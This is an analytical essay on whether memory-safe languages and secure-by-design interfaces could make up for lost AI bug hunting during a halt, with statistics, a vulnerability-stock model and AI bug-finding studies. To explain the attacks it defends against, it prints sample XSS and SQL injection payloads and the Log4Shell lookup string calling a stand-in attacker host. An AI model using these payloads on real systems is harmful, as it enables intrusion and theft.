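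Both companies counted flaws in large products written mostly in C and C++. An online shop written in Java or Python has few memory errors of its own, so rewriting it in Rust would barely change its security. *The AI bugpocalypse is here. Now what?* (Cable, 2026) cites estimates that memory-safe languages could prevent 60–70% of vulnerabilities, but these apply only to products written in memory-unsafe languages. Even in those products, the share of vulnerabilities that are memory errors changes over time, and in Android it fell from 76% to under 20%.

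*Don't Judge an AI-Discovered CVE by Its Category*, by the security company Securin, sorts the vulnerabilities published in 2026 by type of error and attributes 19.0% to memory corruption. If memory errors are 70% of the flaws in C and C++ products and close to zero elsewhere, a rough estimate is that those products contribute only 27% of all published vulnerabilities (0.19 / 0.70). A figure that is right for Chrome can therefore be wrong for software as a whole.

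### What attackers exploit

Many published vulnerabilities are never exploited, so the flaws used in real attacks are a better guide to the danger. *Look What You Made Us Patch* (Charrier, Sadowski and colleagues, 2026) counted 90 vulnerabilities that attackers exploited in 2025 before a patch was public. About 35% were memory errors. If memory-safe languages had prevented all of those, about 58 vulnerabilities would have remained.

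The rest included injection flaws, in which a program runs an attacker's data as commands, and flaws that let attackers bypass logins and permission checks. These were common in products that companies buy to run or protect their networks. Of the 90 vulnerabilities, 43 were in these products, the highest number Google has recorded, and 21 of those were in security and networking equipment. Browsers accounted for less than 10% of the 90. Charrier and colleagues take this as a sign that browser hardening works, but they also think attackers have become better at hiding.

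Memory corruption's share is lower still in Securin's figures for 2026. It made up 9.5% of the vulnerabilities that people had turned into working attacks, while injection made up 24.3%. Google's list contains only flaws that attackers used before a patch existed, often in phones and operating systems, where C and C++ are common. Securin covers a wider range of software.

| Group of vulnerabilities | Share that are memory errors |
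|---|---:|
| Microsoft products, 2006–2018 | about 70% |
| Chromium, high and critical severity, 2015–2020 | about 70% |
| Found by AI, 2026 (Securin) | 57.7% |
| Exploited before a patch, 2025 (Charrier and colleagues) | about 35% |
| All published, 2026 (Securin) | 19.0% |
| Turned into working attacks, 2026 (Securin) | 9.5% |

The large share of memory errors among AI-found flaws probably reflects where researchers look, as it does in Anthropic's public list. Injection flaws make up only 3.8% of the AI-found flaws, but AI can find them too. *AI-Found Vulnerabilities More Likely to Enable RCE, Google Says* (Mascellino, 2026) reports that an AI system from Hacktron AI found a command injection flaw in BeyondTrust's remote-access software without human direction. One group of attackers exploited it within four days of disclosure, and five more groups followed within seven days.

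Counting flaws one by one may understate what memory safety achieves, because attacks on phones and browsers often need several vulnerabilities in a row. If an attack needs three, and each has a 35% chance of being a memory error, there is a 73% chance (1 − 0.65³) that at least one is, and the attack fails without it. Attackers would look for a replacement but would have fewer flaws to choose from. The argument does not apply where a single flaw in a company's network equipment lets anyone in.

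### How Google prevents cross-site scripting

Cross-site scripting, or XSS, happens when a website inserts text from one person into a page and another person's browser runs it as code. Suppose a site greets its users by name:

```js
greeting.innerHTML = "Hello, " + name;
```

An attacker can register under the name `<img src=x onerror="steal()">`. The browser tries to load an image that does not exist, and the failure triggers the attacker's code. That code runs with the permissions of whoever is viewing the page, so it can read their messages or change their settings.

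A site can repair this flaw by replacing each `<` with `&lt;`, so that the browser displays the character instead of treating it as the start of a command. But a large site inserts text in thousands of places, and the correct replacement is different inside a link or a script, so programmers who have to remember this every time will sometimes forget.

Google moved the decision into its programming interfaces. Its libraries have a special type, `SafeHtml`, for text that a browser may interpret. Ordinary code can create such a value only through approved functions, which neutralise dangerous characters or remove dangerous parts. The functions that write to a page accept only this type. In simplified form:

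```ts
setHtml(greeting, "Hello, " + name);               // does not compile
setHtml(greeting, htmlEscape("Hello, " + name));   // compiles
```

A compile-time check also stops programmers from using `innerHTML` directly instead of the library. Those who need an exception must request a security review, so reviewers can concentrate on a few places, much as they do with unsafe code in Rust.

*If It's Not Secure, It Should Not Compile* (Wang, Bangert and Kern, 2021) reports fewer XSS vulnerabilities in Google's code over two years of enforcing these rules. Tens of thousands of engineers worked under them without a significant loss of productivity. Google's *Secure by Design* (2024) bases its argument for memory-safe languages on decades of experience addressing other large classes of vulnerability that were once about as common as memory errors.

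Like Android's results, this is a before-and-after comparison from one company, and other changes may have helped. Google also has a shared code base where it can impose a check on everyone. A small company that builds its site from dozens of outside packages would find this much harder.

### SQL injection and default passwords

SQL injection is the same mistake in a database query. A program might look up a user by joining pieces of text:

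```js
query = "SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '" + name + "'";
```

If a program inserts a name typed by a user directly into a database query, someone can enter `' OR '1'='1`, which makes the query's condition true for every record, and the database returns all of them. The standard remedy is a parameterised query, which sends the command and the name separately, so the database never treats the name as part of the command. Google's libraries go further and accept only query text that the programmer wrote into the program, unless a reviewer has approved an exception.

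Programmers have known this remedy for decades, but SQL injection still does great damage. In 2023 criminals used an SQL injection vulnerability in MOVEit, a file-transfer program, to steal data from more than 2,000 organisations. Injection of all kinds makes up 20.1% of the vulnerabilities in Securin's 2026 figures. A government that wanted quick results during a halt could therefore do a lot just by getting companies to use existing remedies.

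Eliminating default passwords requires no new programming method. In 2016 the Mirai malware took over hundreds of thousands of cameras and routers by trying about 60 factory-set username and password combinations. Manufacturers can give each device its own password or make the owner choose one before the device works. The UK has required one or the other for consumer devices since April 2024.

### Rules that belong to one program

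Each of these remedies enforces a rule that applies to almost any program. Hellerstein (2026), in *No Room for Bugs*, calls such rules universal properties and contrasts them with rules specific to one program, such as "every voter can only vote once". A compiler can forbid the use of freed memory whatever the program is for, but it can enforce the voting rule only if someone has written that rule in a form the compiler can check.

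Missing permission checks are the most familiar example. This Rust function has no memory error:

```rust
fn show_invoice(user: &User, id: u64) -> Invoice {
    database.load_invoice(id)   // never checks who owns it
}
```

If a web application does not check permissions, a customer can read someone else's invoice by changing the invoice number in the web address. A framework can reduce this risk by refusing every request for which the programmer has not named a required permission. This catches forgotten checks but not wrong ones. Cable points out that a check may look reasonable on its own and still break a company's rules about who may see what, and that someone can know the programming language without knowing those rules.

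Programs can also accept a valid message at the wrong time. In 2018 a researcher found that attackers could log in without a password to servers using libssh, a library for encrypted logins. Normally the server checks the password and then sends the client a message saying that the login succeeded. If an attacker sent that message to the server, the server let the attacker in. Rust's types can represent each stage of a login so that the compiler rejects steps in the wrong order, but programmers still have to describe the stages correctly.

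A correct program can still be insecure if its owner sets it up badly. For example, a company may leave a folder of customer records open to the whole internet because an employee needed to share one file. Safe default settings help, but the owner must be able to change them, and a compiler cannot check whether a folder is supposed to be public.

Other attacks need no flaw in the software. An attacker may buy a stolen password, or phone a help desk and pose as an employee who has lost theirs. Neither Rust nor finding every vulnerability in the company's programs would stop this. Secure design can prevent some of it. Security keys and passkeys prove a user's identity only to the real website, so an attacker can't use a fake login page to collect anything reusable. Google said in 2018 that none of its more than 85,000 employees had lost a work account to phishing since it began requiring security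 keys in early 2017. But a help desk that resets accounts after a persuasive phone call can undo this protection.

### Log4Shell

Log4Shell, one of the most serious vulnerabilities of recent years, was in Log4j, a Java library that programs use to record events such as failed logins. Log4j had a feature called lookups, which replaced certain expressions in a log message with other information. From 2013, one kind of lookup could fetch that information from another computer.

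In December 2021 the public learned what this allowed. An attacker could type the following into a login form, a chat window or any other field that a program might log:

```text
${jndi:ldap://attacker.example/a}
```

When Log4j recorded the text, it recognised the expression and contacted the attacker's server. The server could reply with the location of Java code, which the program loaded and ran. The attacker needed no password. Log4j was in so many products that many companies did not know whether they had it. The vulnerability received the highest severity score, 10 out of 10.

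Java's memory protection worked throughout. Log4j was carrying out a feature that its developers had added on purpose, so it did not crash or read past the end of a buffer. An ordinary fuzzer could have logged the dangerous text without detecting a fault. At the 2016 Black Hat security conference, researchers had presented the general technique of abusing Java's lookup system to run code, but Log4j's flaw went unreported for another five years.

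A rule like Google's for XSS could have prevented Log4Shell. If Log4j had interpreted expressions only in text written by programmers, a stranger's message would have stayed plain text. But someone would first have had to realise that a logging library needed such a rule. Secure design works well against dangers people have recognised, but much less well against features that seem harmless and turn out to be dangerous.

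### Four ways to look for logic flaws

Finding a logic flaw automatically requires an oracle, a check that can tell a wrong result from a right one. A crash is an easy oracle for many memory errors, but a logic flaw usually produces an ordinary-looking result.

matklad (2026), in *Finding Bugs*, discusses an example from Rust's `regex` library, which searches text for patterns. One version returned only `b` for a search that should have matched all of `zabb`. Another developer's general fuzzer had missed the bug for lack of an oracle. A fuzzer that matklad wrote for the purpose found it, along with another bug, though matklad admits that knowing what to look for made this easier. For a search algorithm, engineers can use differential testing against a slow, simple version. There is no simple second version of a company's rules about who may read which invoice. Drescher (2026), in *How To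 Fuzz for Logic Bugs?*, argues that logic flaws are getting more attention as memory-safe languages spread, and uses browsers' separation of websites as a case study in building effective oracles.

In December 2026 Anthropic published a comparison of four ways to search for such flaws with AI models:

- In agentic code review, the model reads the code, guesses where it might break a rule and tests the guess.
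- In an informal correctness proof, the model argues step by step that the code obeys the rule. A step that fails may point to a bug.
- In AI-assisted fuzzing, the model helps to set up a fuzzer and writes checks for it.
- In symbolic execution, a tool treats the input as an unknown, as in algebra, and tries to solve for a value that breaks the rule.

*Anthropic's AI bug tests uncover previously undisclosed flaws* (Pogorelec, 2026) describes the test. The researchers chose 21 bugs that had already been repaired: nine in the database SQLite, eight in image-png, a Rust library for reading images, and four in data compression software (three in zstd and one in Brotli). The model received the source code from before the repair. It could submit up to 1,000 inputs per run, and the researchers counted a bug as found if any input produced different results in the old and repaired versions. They ran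 each method three times on each bug.

In half of the trials the model had only the code and had to work out the rule for itself. In the other half the researchers also told it which rule the code should obey. The results for Claude Mythos 5 were:

| Method | Bugs found from code alone | Bugs found with the rule supplied |
|---|---:|---:|
| Agentic code review | 11 | 20 |
| Informal correctness proof | 8 | 21 |
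| Symbolic execution | 0 | 13 |
| AI-assisted fuzzing | 0 | 1 |

With only 21 bugs, the difference between 11 and 8 could easily be chance. The gap between reading the code and using the heavier tools is much clearer. The 13 for symbolic execution overstates what the tool contributed, because the model found those bugs while reading the source code and the tool confirmed only two of them.

The simplest methods did best because they rely on what the models are good at. According to the researchers, the models can infer what code is meant to do, form a theory about how it might fail and test it. A fuzzer can try millions of inputs, but it can detect a wrong answer only if someone has written a check for it. Even with that check, it may never try the rare input that produces the wrong answer. Symbolic execution can target such an input, but the number of paths through a program quickly becomes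 too large to follow.

Supplying the rule produced the biggest gain, raising the score from 11 to 20 for code review and from 8 to 21 for informal proofs. This fits Tolmach and Klaus's view that the hard part of verification is now deciding what to prove, more than constructing the proof. During a training-only halt, developers could write down their programs' rules for existing models to check. The gain would probably be smaller than in the test, where the researchers supplied exactly the rule that the code broke. A developer would have to list hundreds of rules without knowing which one mattered, and might leave it out.

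Newer models also did much better at code review when given only the code. Claude Sonnet 4.5 found one of the 21 bugs, Claude Opus 4.5 found five, Claude Opus 5.5 found 13 and Claude Mythos 5.2 found 15. Opus 4.5 came out in November 2025, so about a year of training roughly tripled the number of bugs found. A training-only halt that began then would have denied defenders this large improvement. However, newer models have memorized some of the old bugs from their training data, which may explain part of the improvement.

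### New flaws in macOS and Linux

During the tests, the models also found 316 other bugs in the same projects, 127 of which were neither fixed nor already known. Anthropic separately searched current software and found the Rust compiler flaw and serious flaws in macOS and Linux.

*Linux, к твоему контролёру есть вопросы* (Antipov, 2026) describes the macOS flaw, which was in a helper program for Finder, the Mac's file manager. The helper runs with full administrator rights, and any user of the computer could make it change the owner of system files and then take complete control. Apple's newer hardware protections for memory did not prevent this, because the flaw did not involve misuse of memory. A related timing flaw in Caliptra, an open-source security component for chips, let an attacker swap the firmware after the component checked it but before it was loaded.

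The largest group of findings was in Linux's eBPF verifier. eBPF lets people load small programs into the kernel, for example to filter network traffic. Since a bad program could take over the computer, the verifier examines each program once, when it loads, and works out which values every variable could have. It rejects the program if any of those values could lead to a forbidden memory access.

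A mistake that kernel developers fixed in 2017 shows how this reasoning can go wrong. The example comes from Yu (2026), in *Evolution of Value Tracking in the BPF Verifier*. A processor can read the same 64 bits as a signed number, which may be negative, or as an unsigned one, which may not. The bits for −8 are also the bits for an enormous positive number. The program in the example checks a value twice:

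```text
reject if value > largest possible number   (unsigned)
reject if value > 1                         (signed)
write to memory at start + value
```

Every value passes the first check, including −8. But the old Linux verifier kept only one minimum and one maximum for each value. It set the minimum to 0 after the first check and the maximum to 1 after the signed check, so it concluded that the value had to be 0 or 1 and allowed the write. Because −8 also passes the signed check, the program could write eight bytes before the start of its memory. Linux now tracks the signed and unsigned ranges separately.

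Claude's informal proofs exposed more than 100 errors in the current verifier's logic. One of them, CVE-2026-98041, dated from 2020 and let a local user gain higher privileges. The verifier used the fact that a certain pointer is never zero, but applied it to a comparison of only 32 of the pointer's 64 bits. Those 32 bits can all be zero even when the whole pointer is not, so the verifier accepted a dangerous memory read. Kernel developers have received all the reports and have been releasing fixes for several months.

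The verifier is written in C, but a Rust version with the same logic errors would accept the same dangerous programs. A memory-safe language protects the verifier's own memory but does not correct how it checks other people's code.

Similar flaws occur in code already written in Rust. *AI meets Cryptography 2* (Chaliasos and Pham, 2026) describes using an AI auditor on OpenVM, a Rust project for proving that a computation ran correctly. One of OpenVM's libraries did not test whether a number supplied by the party being checked was of the right kind, so a dishonest party could forge a result. Human reviewers confirmed the flaw before reporting it, and OpenVM has fixed it.

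Attackers can also use AI to exploit logic flaws. The Next Web reported that criminals had used AI to help build an attack on a previously unknown design flaw in which the developer had hard-coded a trust assumption.

### What could replace the models

AI bug hunting has fewer substitutes for finding logic flaws than for finding memory errors. If a halt makes AI models unavailable, fuzzers, hardened allocators and memory tagging still help with memory errors, but none of them can detect a flaw that lets a customer read the wrong invoice. Human experts can find logic flaws by reading code, and companies already pay outsiders to report them, but few people have the skill and each review takes time.

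Defenders could preserve part of the models' work by having the models write tests before a halt. An earlier agent from Anthropic read the names, comments and type descriptions in existing code, worked out general properties that the code should have, and wrote tests for them. For example, a sorting function's output should have the same items as its input. An ordinary testing tool can then check the property on many generated inputs without an AI model. *The Jagged Neurosymbolic Frontier* recommends a similar division of labour, in which models write down their assumptions and a fuzzer searches for inputs that violate them, because AI audits alone can be unpredictable and expensive.

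Such tests would keep working throughout a halt on training and use, and catch some new mistakes as programmers changed the code. They would not supply the rules for a new feature. Fuzzing also did poorly in Anthropic's comparison even when the model had the rule, so people would still have to find many rare violations themselves.

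## How much AI bug hunting prevention could replace

No published work appears to estimate directly how far prevention could make up for lost AI bug hunting. A rough answer has to combine the two closest sources, which each cover half of the question. Google simulated what happens when programmers change languages while people keep finding flaws at the same rate. Chauvin's *Vulnerabilities and exploits* estimates how much existing AI models have left for later ones to find, but does not discuss languages.

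### The methods compared

| Method | Flaws covered | Speed | Main cost | Reaches old code | Needs AI |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| AI bug hunting | Memory errors, many logic flaws | Days to find, often months to repair | Checking and repairs | Yes | Yes |
| Memory-safe languages for new code | Memory errors | Years | Training programmers | No | No |
| AI rewriting in Rust | Memory errors | Weeks to write, longer to test and adopt | Checking the result | Yes | Yes, until the rewrite is done |
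| Hardening | Some memory errors | Months, through updates | A small slowdown | Yes | No |
| Formal verification | Any property someone can state | Weeks with AI, years without | Writing and renewing proofs | Yes | In practice, yes |
| Safe interfaces for web pages and databases | Injection flaws | Years | Changing code that uses the old interfaces | Only where programmers convert it | No |

Three of these methods (bug hunting, rewriting and proof) can remove flaws from old code on a large scale. All three depend on AI for their speed, so a halt on training and use would slow them all. Hardening would still protect old code, but it leaves the flaws in place. The main remaining way to reduce the number of memory errors would be to stop adding new ones while human experts and fuzzers worked through the old ones.

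### A model of the stock

The following model is an illustration with mostly invented numbers, not a published result. Let N be the number of memory-safety vulnerabilities in a large program, r the number that programmers add each year, and L the mean vulnerability lifetime in years, as in the calculations for Android. The stock changes at the rate

dN/dt = r − N/L

Start with the earlier example's r = 100 and L = 2.5, which keep the stock steady at 250. Now compare three changes, each starting today:

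- Programmers stop writing new unsafe code at once, so r drops to zero and N = 250e^(−t/2.5).
- They phase it out evenly over ten years, which gives N = 312.5 − 25t − 62.5e^(−t/2.5) during that time.
- Programmers change nothing, but better AI halves L to 1.25 years, so N = 125 + 125e^(−t/1.25).

| Vulnerabilities left | After 1 year | After 3 years | After 5 years |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| No change | 250 | 250 | 250 |
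| New unsafe code stops at once | 168 | 75 | 34 |
| Ten-year phase-out | 246 | 219 | 179 |
| Better AI halves L | 181 | 136 | 127 |

Immediately stopping new vulnerabilities and using better AI to find bugs both start by reducing the stock at a rate of 100 a year, the first by adding nothing to it and the second by doubling repairs. The immediate stop then moves ahead and stays ahead, because the better search still has to deal with 100 new vulnerabilities every year. After t years, the immediate stop leaves 125(1 − e^(−t/2.5))² fewer vulnerabilities than better AI does.

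The ten-year phase-out overtakes better AI only after 7.4 years, more than two years after even a five-year halt would have ended. After one year, it achieves 6% of the reduction that better AI would have achieved, rising to 28% after three years and 58% after five. The immediate stop achieves 120%, 154% and 176% at the same points.

These percentages depend on L. If L starts at 4.1 years, the mean that Alexopoulos and colleagues found across their 11 projects, the phase-out replaces 46% after five years. At OpenSSL's 7.1 years, it replaces 37%. *Open Source, Open Threats?* (2025) reports average lifespans of 847 to 1,473 days (2.3 to 4.0 years) in different collections of open-source packages, so the starting value of 2.5 years is again near the low end.

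The model also holds the amount of new code constant. In a growing code base, like the one in Google's simulation, prevention would do better because there would be more new flaws to prevent.

Prevention also leaves maintainers with fewer repairs, an advantage that the stock does not show. Over the five years, they would have to repair 623 vulnerabilities with better AI, 500 if nothing changed, and 216 after an immediate stop. Large companies can handle a surge, as Mozilla did in April. But the journalist Maggie Miller (2026), in *Cyber experts warn AI is overwhelming their response to system flaws*, reported in August that new models were identifying vulnerabilities faster than defenders could fix them. If repairs take up part of L, doubling the speed of the search does not halve L. Suppose a vulnerability takes two years to find and another six months to repair. A search twice as fast reduces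 L from 2.5 years to 1.5, and the stock settles at 150 instead of the 125 it would reach if L were halved.

### What later models would add

Chauvin's estimate suggests that later AI models may have less to offer than the model assumes. He thinks Mythos Preview, together with earlier models and methods, probably found 70–80% of the severe vulnerabilities in the code it reviewed. Nobody had searched most of that code properly before, so Mythos Preview found many easy flaws. If he is right, no later model could find as many old flaws in that code. Chauvin calls his estimate a best guess and expects some exceptions, such as use-after-free errors and flaws that depend on exact timing.

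Firefox offers a partial check on Chauvin's estimate. Mythos Preview found 180 high-severity vulnerabilities for Firefox 150. If those were 70–80% of the total, between 45 and 77 would have been left. Half a year later, OpenAI released GPT-6 Cyber, a version of GPT-6 Astra tuned for security work. It had found 81 more Firefox vulnerabilities that Mozilla rated high severity, according to Bot Mutiny's *OpenAI Releases GPT-6 Cyber to Approved Defenders and Rates It Critical* (2026). Firefox 159 alone fixed 108 high-severity vulnerabilities, possibly including some of those 81. Some of the later vulnerabilities may come from code that Mozilla wrote after April, but Chauvin's estimate still looks too high for Firefox.

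The same release shows the kind of capability a halt would keep from attackers. The Hacker News' *OpenAI Launches GPT-6 Cyber After AI Helps Find 81 Firefox Flaws* (2026) reports that GPT-6 Cyber turned 948 Linux vulnerabilities into working attacks. The older GPT-5.6 Sol did so for 166 with the same research software.

Defenders could partly make up for the missing models by improving the software around existing ones. Aspen Digital, a programme of the Aspen Institute, describes how Niels Provos used such software to reproduce some of Mythos Preview's findings with two weaker models, Claude Opus 4.6 and Sonnet 4.6. Reproducing a known result is easier than getting it first, so his work does not prove that the weaker models could have replaced Mythos Preview, but it suggests that L could keep falling during a training-only halt.

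### Flaws that only AI finds

Changing language does not remove flaws already in old code that people and fuzzers never find. Suppose the program contains H such flaws in addition to the ordinary 250, and better AI removes them as quickly as the others. The immediate stop is ahead of better AI only if H is below about 25 after one year, 67 after three years and 95 after five. Better AI is therefore about level after one year if there is one hidden flaw for every ten ordinary ones, and after five years if there are almost four.

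Nobody has measured H, but the age of ordinary bugs gives some idea of how uneven the search is. Pebblebed's *Kernel bugs hide for 2 years on average. Some hide for 20* analysed about 125,000 Linux kernel bugs whose fixes named the change that introduced them. The mean lifetime was 2.1 years and the median was 0.7 years. About 4.2% of the bugs lasted more than ten years, almost five times the 0.9% that the simple model, an exponential curve with the same mean, predicts.

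One of them, from 2006, was in the code that tracks network connections. A programmer fixing another problem removed a line that reduced a counter, so under rare conditions the kernel never released a piece of memory. Reproducing the error took about 20 minutes of running one test in a loop while memory was short. Nobody fixed it until August 2025.

Most of the bugs in Pebblebed's data are not known to be vulnerabilities, and only 158 have a CVE number. People eventually found all the bugs in the data, mostly before AI models were good at finding bugs. The data show that some flaws take far longer to find than others, but not how many would stay hidden without AI.

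### Flaws of other kinds

The model so far covers only memory errors, but better AI can also find logic flaws. In *Defining the memory safe problem*, Gaynor notes that some people expect safer languages to reduce logic flaws too, because they let programmers express their intentions more clearly. He says no empirical evidence supports this yet. He also describes a type of logic flaw that Rust does not prevent, even though its effects resemble those of a memory error. It occurs in browsers, which translate JavaScript into machine code while a page runs. If the translator is faulty, an attacker may be able to make it produce dangerous instructions.

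Let m be the share of memory errors among all vulnerabilities, and suppose better AI halves the lifetime of every kind. An immediate stop to new unsafe code then beats better AI only if

m > (1 + e^(−t/2.5)) / 2

The threshold is 84% after one year, 65% after three and 57% after five, and it never drops below 50%. If memory errors are less than half of the problem, better AI always does more than a change of language, however quickly programmers switch.

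The next table shows how much of the reduction from better AI prevention would replace after five years.

| Memory errors as a share of all vulnerabilities | Immediate stop | Ten-year phase-out |
|---|---:|---:|
| 100% (the model so far) | 176% | 58% |
| 70% (Microsoft and Chromium) | 123% | 40% |
| 35% (exploited before a patch in 2025) | 62% | 20% |
| 19% (all published in 2026) | 33% | 11% |

Which row applies depends on the software. The Australian Cyber Security Centre cites an analysis of Mozilla's code in which 32 of 34 critical or high-severity bugs were memory errors. It also cites a finding that memory errors made up 67% of zero-day vulnerabilities in 2021, nearly twice the share for 2025, although the two counts may cover different products. The last row probably fits a web shop better.

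Secure-by-design methods that prevent other flaws would improve the figures. Injection flaws made up 20.1% of the vulnerabilities in Securin's data for 2026. If programmers stopped adding both injection flaws and memory errors at once, prevention would replace 69% of the reduction instead of 33%. The table also counts every vulnerability equally, which understates the value of memory safety in phones and browsers, where memory errors are usually the most dangerous flaws.

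Android shows that memory-safe languages can replace less AI bug hunting once a company has made much of the switch. In 2019 memory errors were 76% of Android's vulnerabilities, so an immediate stop would have replaced 134% of the reduction from better AI after five years. At 20%, slightly above the actual share in 2025, it would replace 35%. Google has already gained most of what memory-safe languages can offer Android. It would keep that gain during a halt, but could not get it a second time to replace lost AI bug hunting.

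Some valuable work remains even in Android. Vander Stoep names firmware, the low-level software that controls a device's hardware, as a particular risk because it has extensive rights and cannot use many of the usual defences. Android's first production Rust driver appeared with version 6.12 of the Linux kernel. For the rest of Android, Google would probably gain more from preventing logic flaws, such as missing permission checks.

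### Devices that seldom receive updates

A patch or a rewritten library protects a device only after someone installs it. For cameras, routers and industrial equipment, getting it installed can take longer than finding the flaw.

*One Bad Apple Spoils the Barrel* (2022) found that third-party components in the firmware of internet-connected devices were on average 5.3 years behind the latest version when the manufacturer released the firmware. Routers tended to be worse than cameras. *AutoFirm* (2024) found that 80% of the known vulnerabilities in such firmware were at least four years old when the firmware came out, and that manufacturers took 1.34 years on average to update a vulnerable library.

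Even manufacturers that issue patches can be slow. *Evaluating the Future Device Security Risk Indicator for Hundreds of IoT Devices* (2022) found that Axis, a network camera maker, took about 953 days on average to patch a vulnerability and more than 16 years in the worst case. Only 370 of the 793 device models in the study had received any patch. *Challenges and Opportunities in Securing the Industrial Internet of Things* (2021) explains that factory operators add to the delay because they first have to test that an update works with their other equipment. Factory machines also stay in use much longer than consumer devices, so manufacturers would have to provide patches for longer.

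If every improvement in the code reaches devices 953 days late, neither an immediate stop nor better AI has helped them after one year. After three years, the devices still have 214 of the original 250 vulnerabilities with the immediate stop and 216 with better AI. After five years, they have 96 and 143, respectively. With a delay of 5.3 years, a device that goes on sale at the end of a five-year halt would still contain components from before the halt began.

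The delay also makes discovery riskier than prevention. Chauvin notes that a patch also reveals the flaw to attackers, so everyone who has not installed it becomes more vulnerable the day it appears. Better AI bug hunting in a shared library could therefore make an old router that uses it less safe for years. Schneier on Security's *Cybersecurity in the Age of Instant Software* predicts that attackers will concentrate on old software whose flaws defenders can find but cannot reliably patch. Replacing devices that run such software, or disconnecting them from the internet, may do more good than safer languages or better bug hunting.

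Phones and browsers are in a much better position. According to Schneier on Security's *What Anthropic’s Mythos Means for the Future of Cybersecurity*, defence will probably benefit in the end, especially where systems are easy to patch and verify.

### The case for prevention

Google's engineers argue that companies have tried the alternatives to memory-safe languages for decades. They first repaired flaws after someone reported them, then added defences that made attacks harder, and later searched for flaws with fuzzers and similar tools. All of this helped, but the work has to be repeated every year. Teams need constant pressure to fuzz their code and fix what they find, and many parts of the code never get tested. Memory-safe languages avoid much of that work in new code.

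Vander Stoep adds that when a program has many memory errors, attackers can combine several of them to get past its other defences. Reducing the number of errors therefore also makes sandboxes and hardened allocators more effective.

The speed of modern attacks strengthens the argument. CERT-EU's *AI is changing the economics of vulnerability discovery. Defenders should adapt now* cites an estimate that attackers exploit a vulnerability on average seven days before a patch exists. Even a quick patch comes too late in such cases, so defenders have to find the flaw before attackers do, or developers have to avoid creating it.

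In the 2026 post *Memory safety is a matter of life and death*, joshlf, a programmer on a security team, makes a moral version of the argument. The post begins with the hacking of a phone belonging to the fiancée of Jamal Khashoggi, the Saudi journalist killed in Istanbul in 2018. As AI bug hunting spreads, joshlf expects few open-source programs in memory-unsafe languages to be safe from catastrophic attacks, and expects some attackers to use such attacks to kill. Memory-safe languages would prevent most of the flaws that allow these attacks, including the most harmful ones, according to joshlf. The post describes Rust as the only language already in production use that does this without making programs slower than C or C++, and concludes that helping Rust succeed is a moral duty.

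To answer programmers who prefer a familiar language, joshlf compares them to a radiologist who chooses a less accurate scanner because it is pleasant to use or reminds them of medical school, which would make a patient's family furious. People who depend on software do not know what a pointer is, joshlf argues, and a programmer's taste should not put them at risk.

The comparison is persuasive for new programs, whose language can still be chosen, but weaker for old ones, because a rewrite takes money and people that could also go into repairs. The post also relies on the 70% figure, which applies mainly to products in C and C++. joshlf expected capable bug-finding agents to become widely available in the summer of 2026, far too soon for a change of language to help much. The argument therefore supports starting early more than it supports switching languages once a halt has begun.

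### The objection that conversion is too slow

Critics of relying on prevention can point to how slowly Android itself adopted Rust. Google had money, expert programmers and a strong commitment, yet Rust made up only 21% of Android's new native code after about three years and just over half of Google's own new native code after six. The model's phase-out, spread evenly over ten years, would have reached 30% and 60% at those points, so Android was, if anything, a little slower than the model assumes.

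The transition also starts slowly in Google's simulation, because it follows an S-shaped curve. If the safe share of new code rises from 12% in year three to 50% in year five and 88% in year seven, the stock is about 204 after five years instead of 179, and prevention replaces only 38% of the reduction from better AI.

Converting old code takes even longer. Bradley and Sastry estimate that experts in Rust, who are scarce and expensive, would typically need several person-years to convert even a moderately sized C program by hand. AI can make this much faster, but a halt on AI use would take away that help.

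Better AI could also help prevent vulnerabilities. Chauvin expects developers to search new code with AI before they release it, so that it ships with few vulnerabilities. The model above leaves this out, because it keeps r at 100 when AI improves. If better AI halved both r and L, the stock would be 147 after one year, 80 after three and 66 after five. For about the first 2.7 years, the stock would be smaller than if developers immediately stopped writing unsafe code. This is a serious problem for anyone who hopes to replace AI bug hunting with prevention during a short halt.

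A quick partial change can answer some of the objection. In the earlier example, where programmers moved half of their new code to Rust at once and went no further, the stock is 209 after one year, 163 after three and 142 after five. That replaces 60%, 77% and 88% of the reduction from better AI (with r still at 100), much more than a complete change spread over ten years. A government preparing for a halt should therefore care more about how much new code changes in the first year than about when the last C++ programmer switches. But few companies could change half their new code in a year unless they had trained their programmers beforehand.

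### Halts of one, three and five years

In a training-only halt, defenders keep the existing models, so the stock of vulnerabilities stays at about 250 without prevention. They lose the reduction that later, better models would have brought, which is 69 vulnerabilities after one year, 114 after three and 123 after five. The first-year figure is probably too high, because it assumes that those models arrive on the first day. If they doubled the repair rate gradually over two years, the loss after one year would be 21, and the ten-year phase-out would replace about a fifth of that loss instead of 6%. The result after five years would hardly change.

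A one-year training-only halt would therefore do limited damage, and better software for existing models might make up for much of it. For memory errors, a realistic shift to memory-safe languages would make up for about a quarter to a third of the loss over three years, and more than half over five. In software where memory errors are only a third of the problem, the shift would make up for about a fifth of the total loss over five years.

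A halt on both training and use is harder to offset because defenders get worse at finding flaws. Suppose, as a guess, that they lose half of their present ability to find and repair flaws, so L doubles to five years. Mozilla might lose more, since AI models found most of the vulnerabilities it fixed in April, while a project that rarely acts on AI reports would lose less. The table compares the results with what would have happened without a halt.

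| Vulnerabilities left | After 1 year | After 3 years | After 5 years |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| No halt, later models halve L | 181 | 136 | 127 |
| Halt on training and use, no prevention | 295 | 363 | 408 |
| The same halt with a ten-year phase-out | 291 | 326 | 316 |
| The same halt with an immediate stop to new unsafe code | 205 | 137 | 92 |

With the ten-year phase-out, the program has more memory errors after five years than it had at the start. Prevention replaces 4% of the loss after one year, 16% after three and 33% after five. Even an immediate stop would take about three years to catch up with the scenario without a halt, because people are removing the old flaws slowly.

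People could get better at finding bugs without AI, though. Pebblebed found that people took a year or less to fix 31% of the Linux bugs introduced in 2014 and 69% of those introduced in 2022, and it lists better fuzzers, error detectors and review as likely causes. The 2022 figure may fall as people find more bugs from that year. If a government paid for more of this work and L rose to only 3.5 years instead of five, the stock after five years with the phase-out would be about 244, slightly below its starting level. During a halt on training and use, money for fuzzing and human experts would therefore protect old code sooner than the same money spent on a slow change of language.
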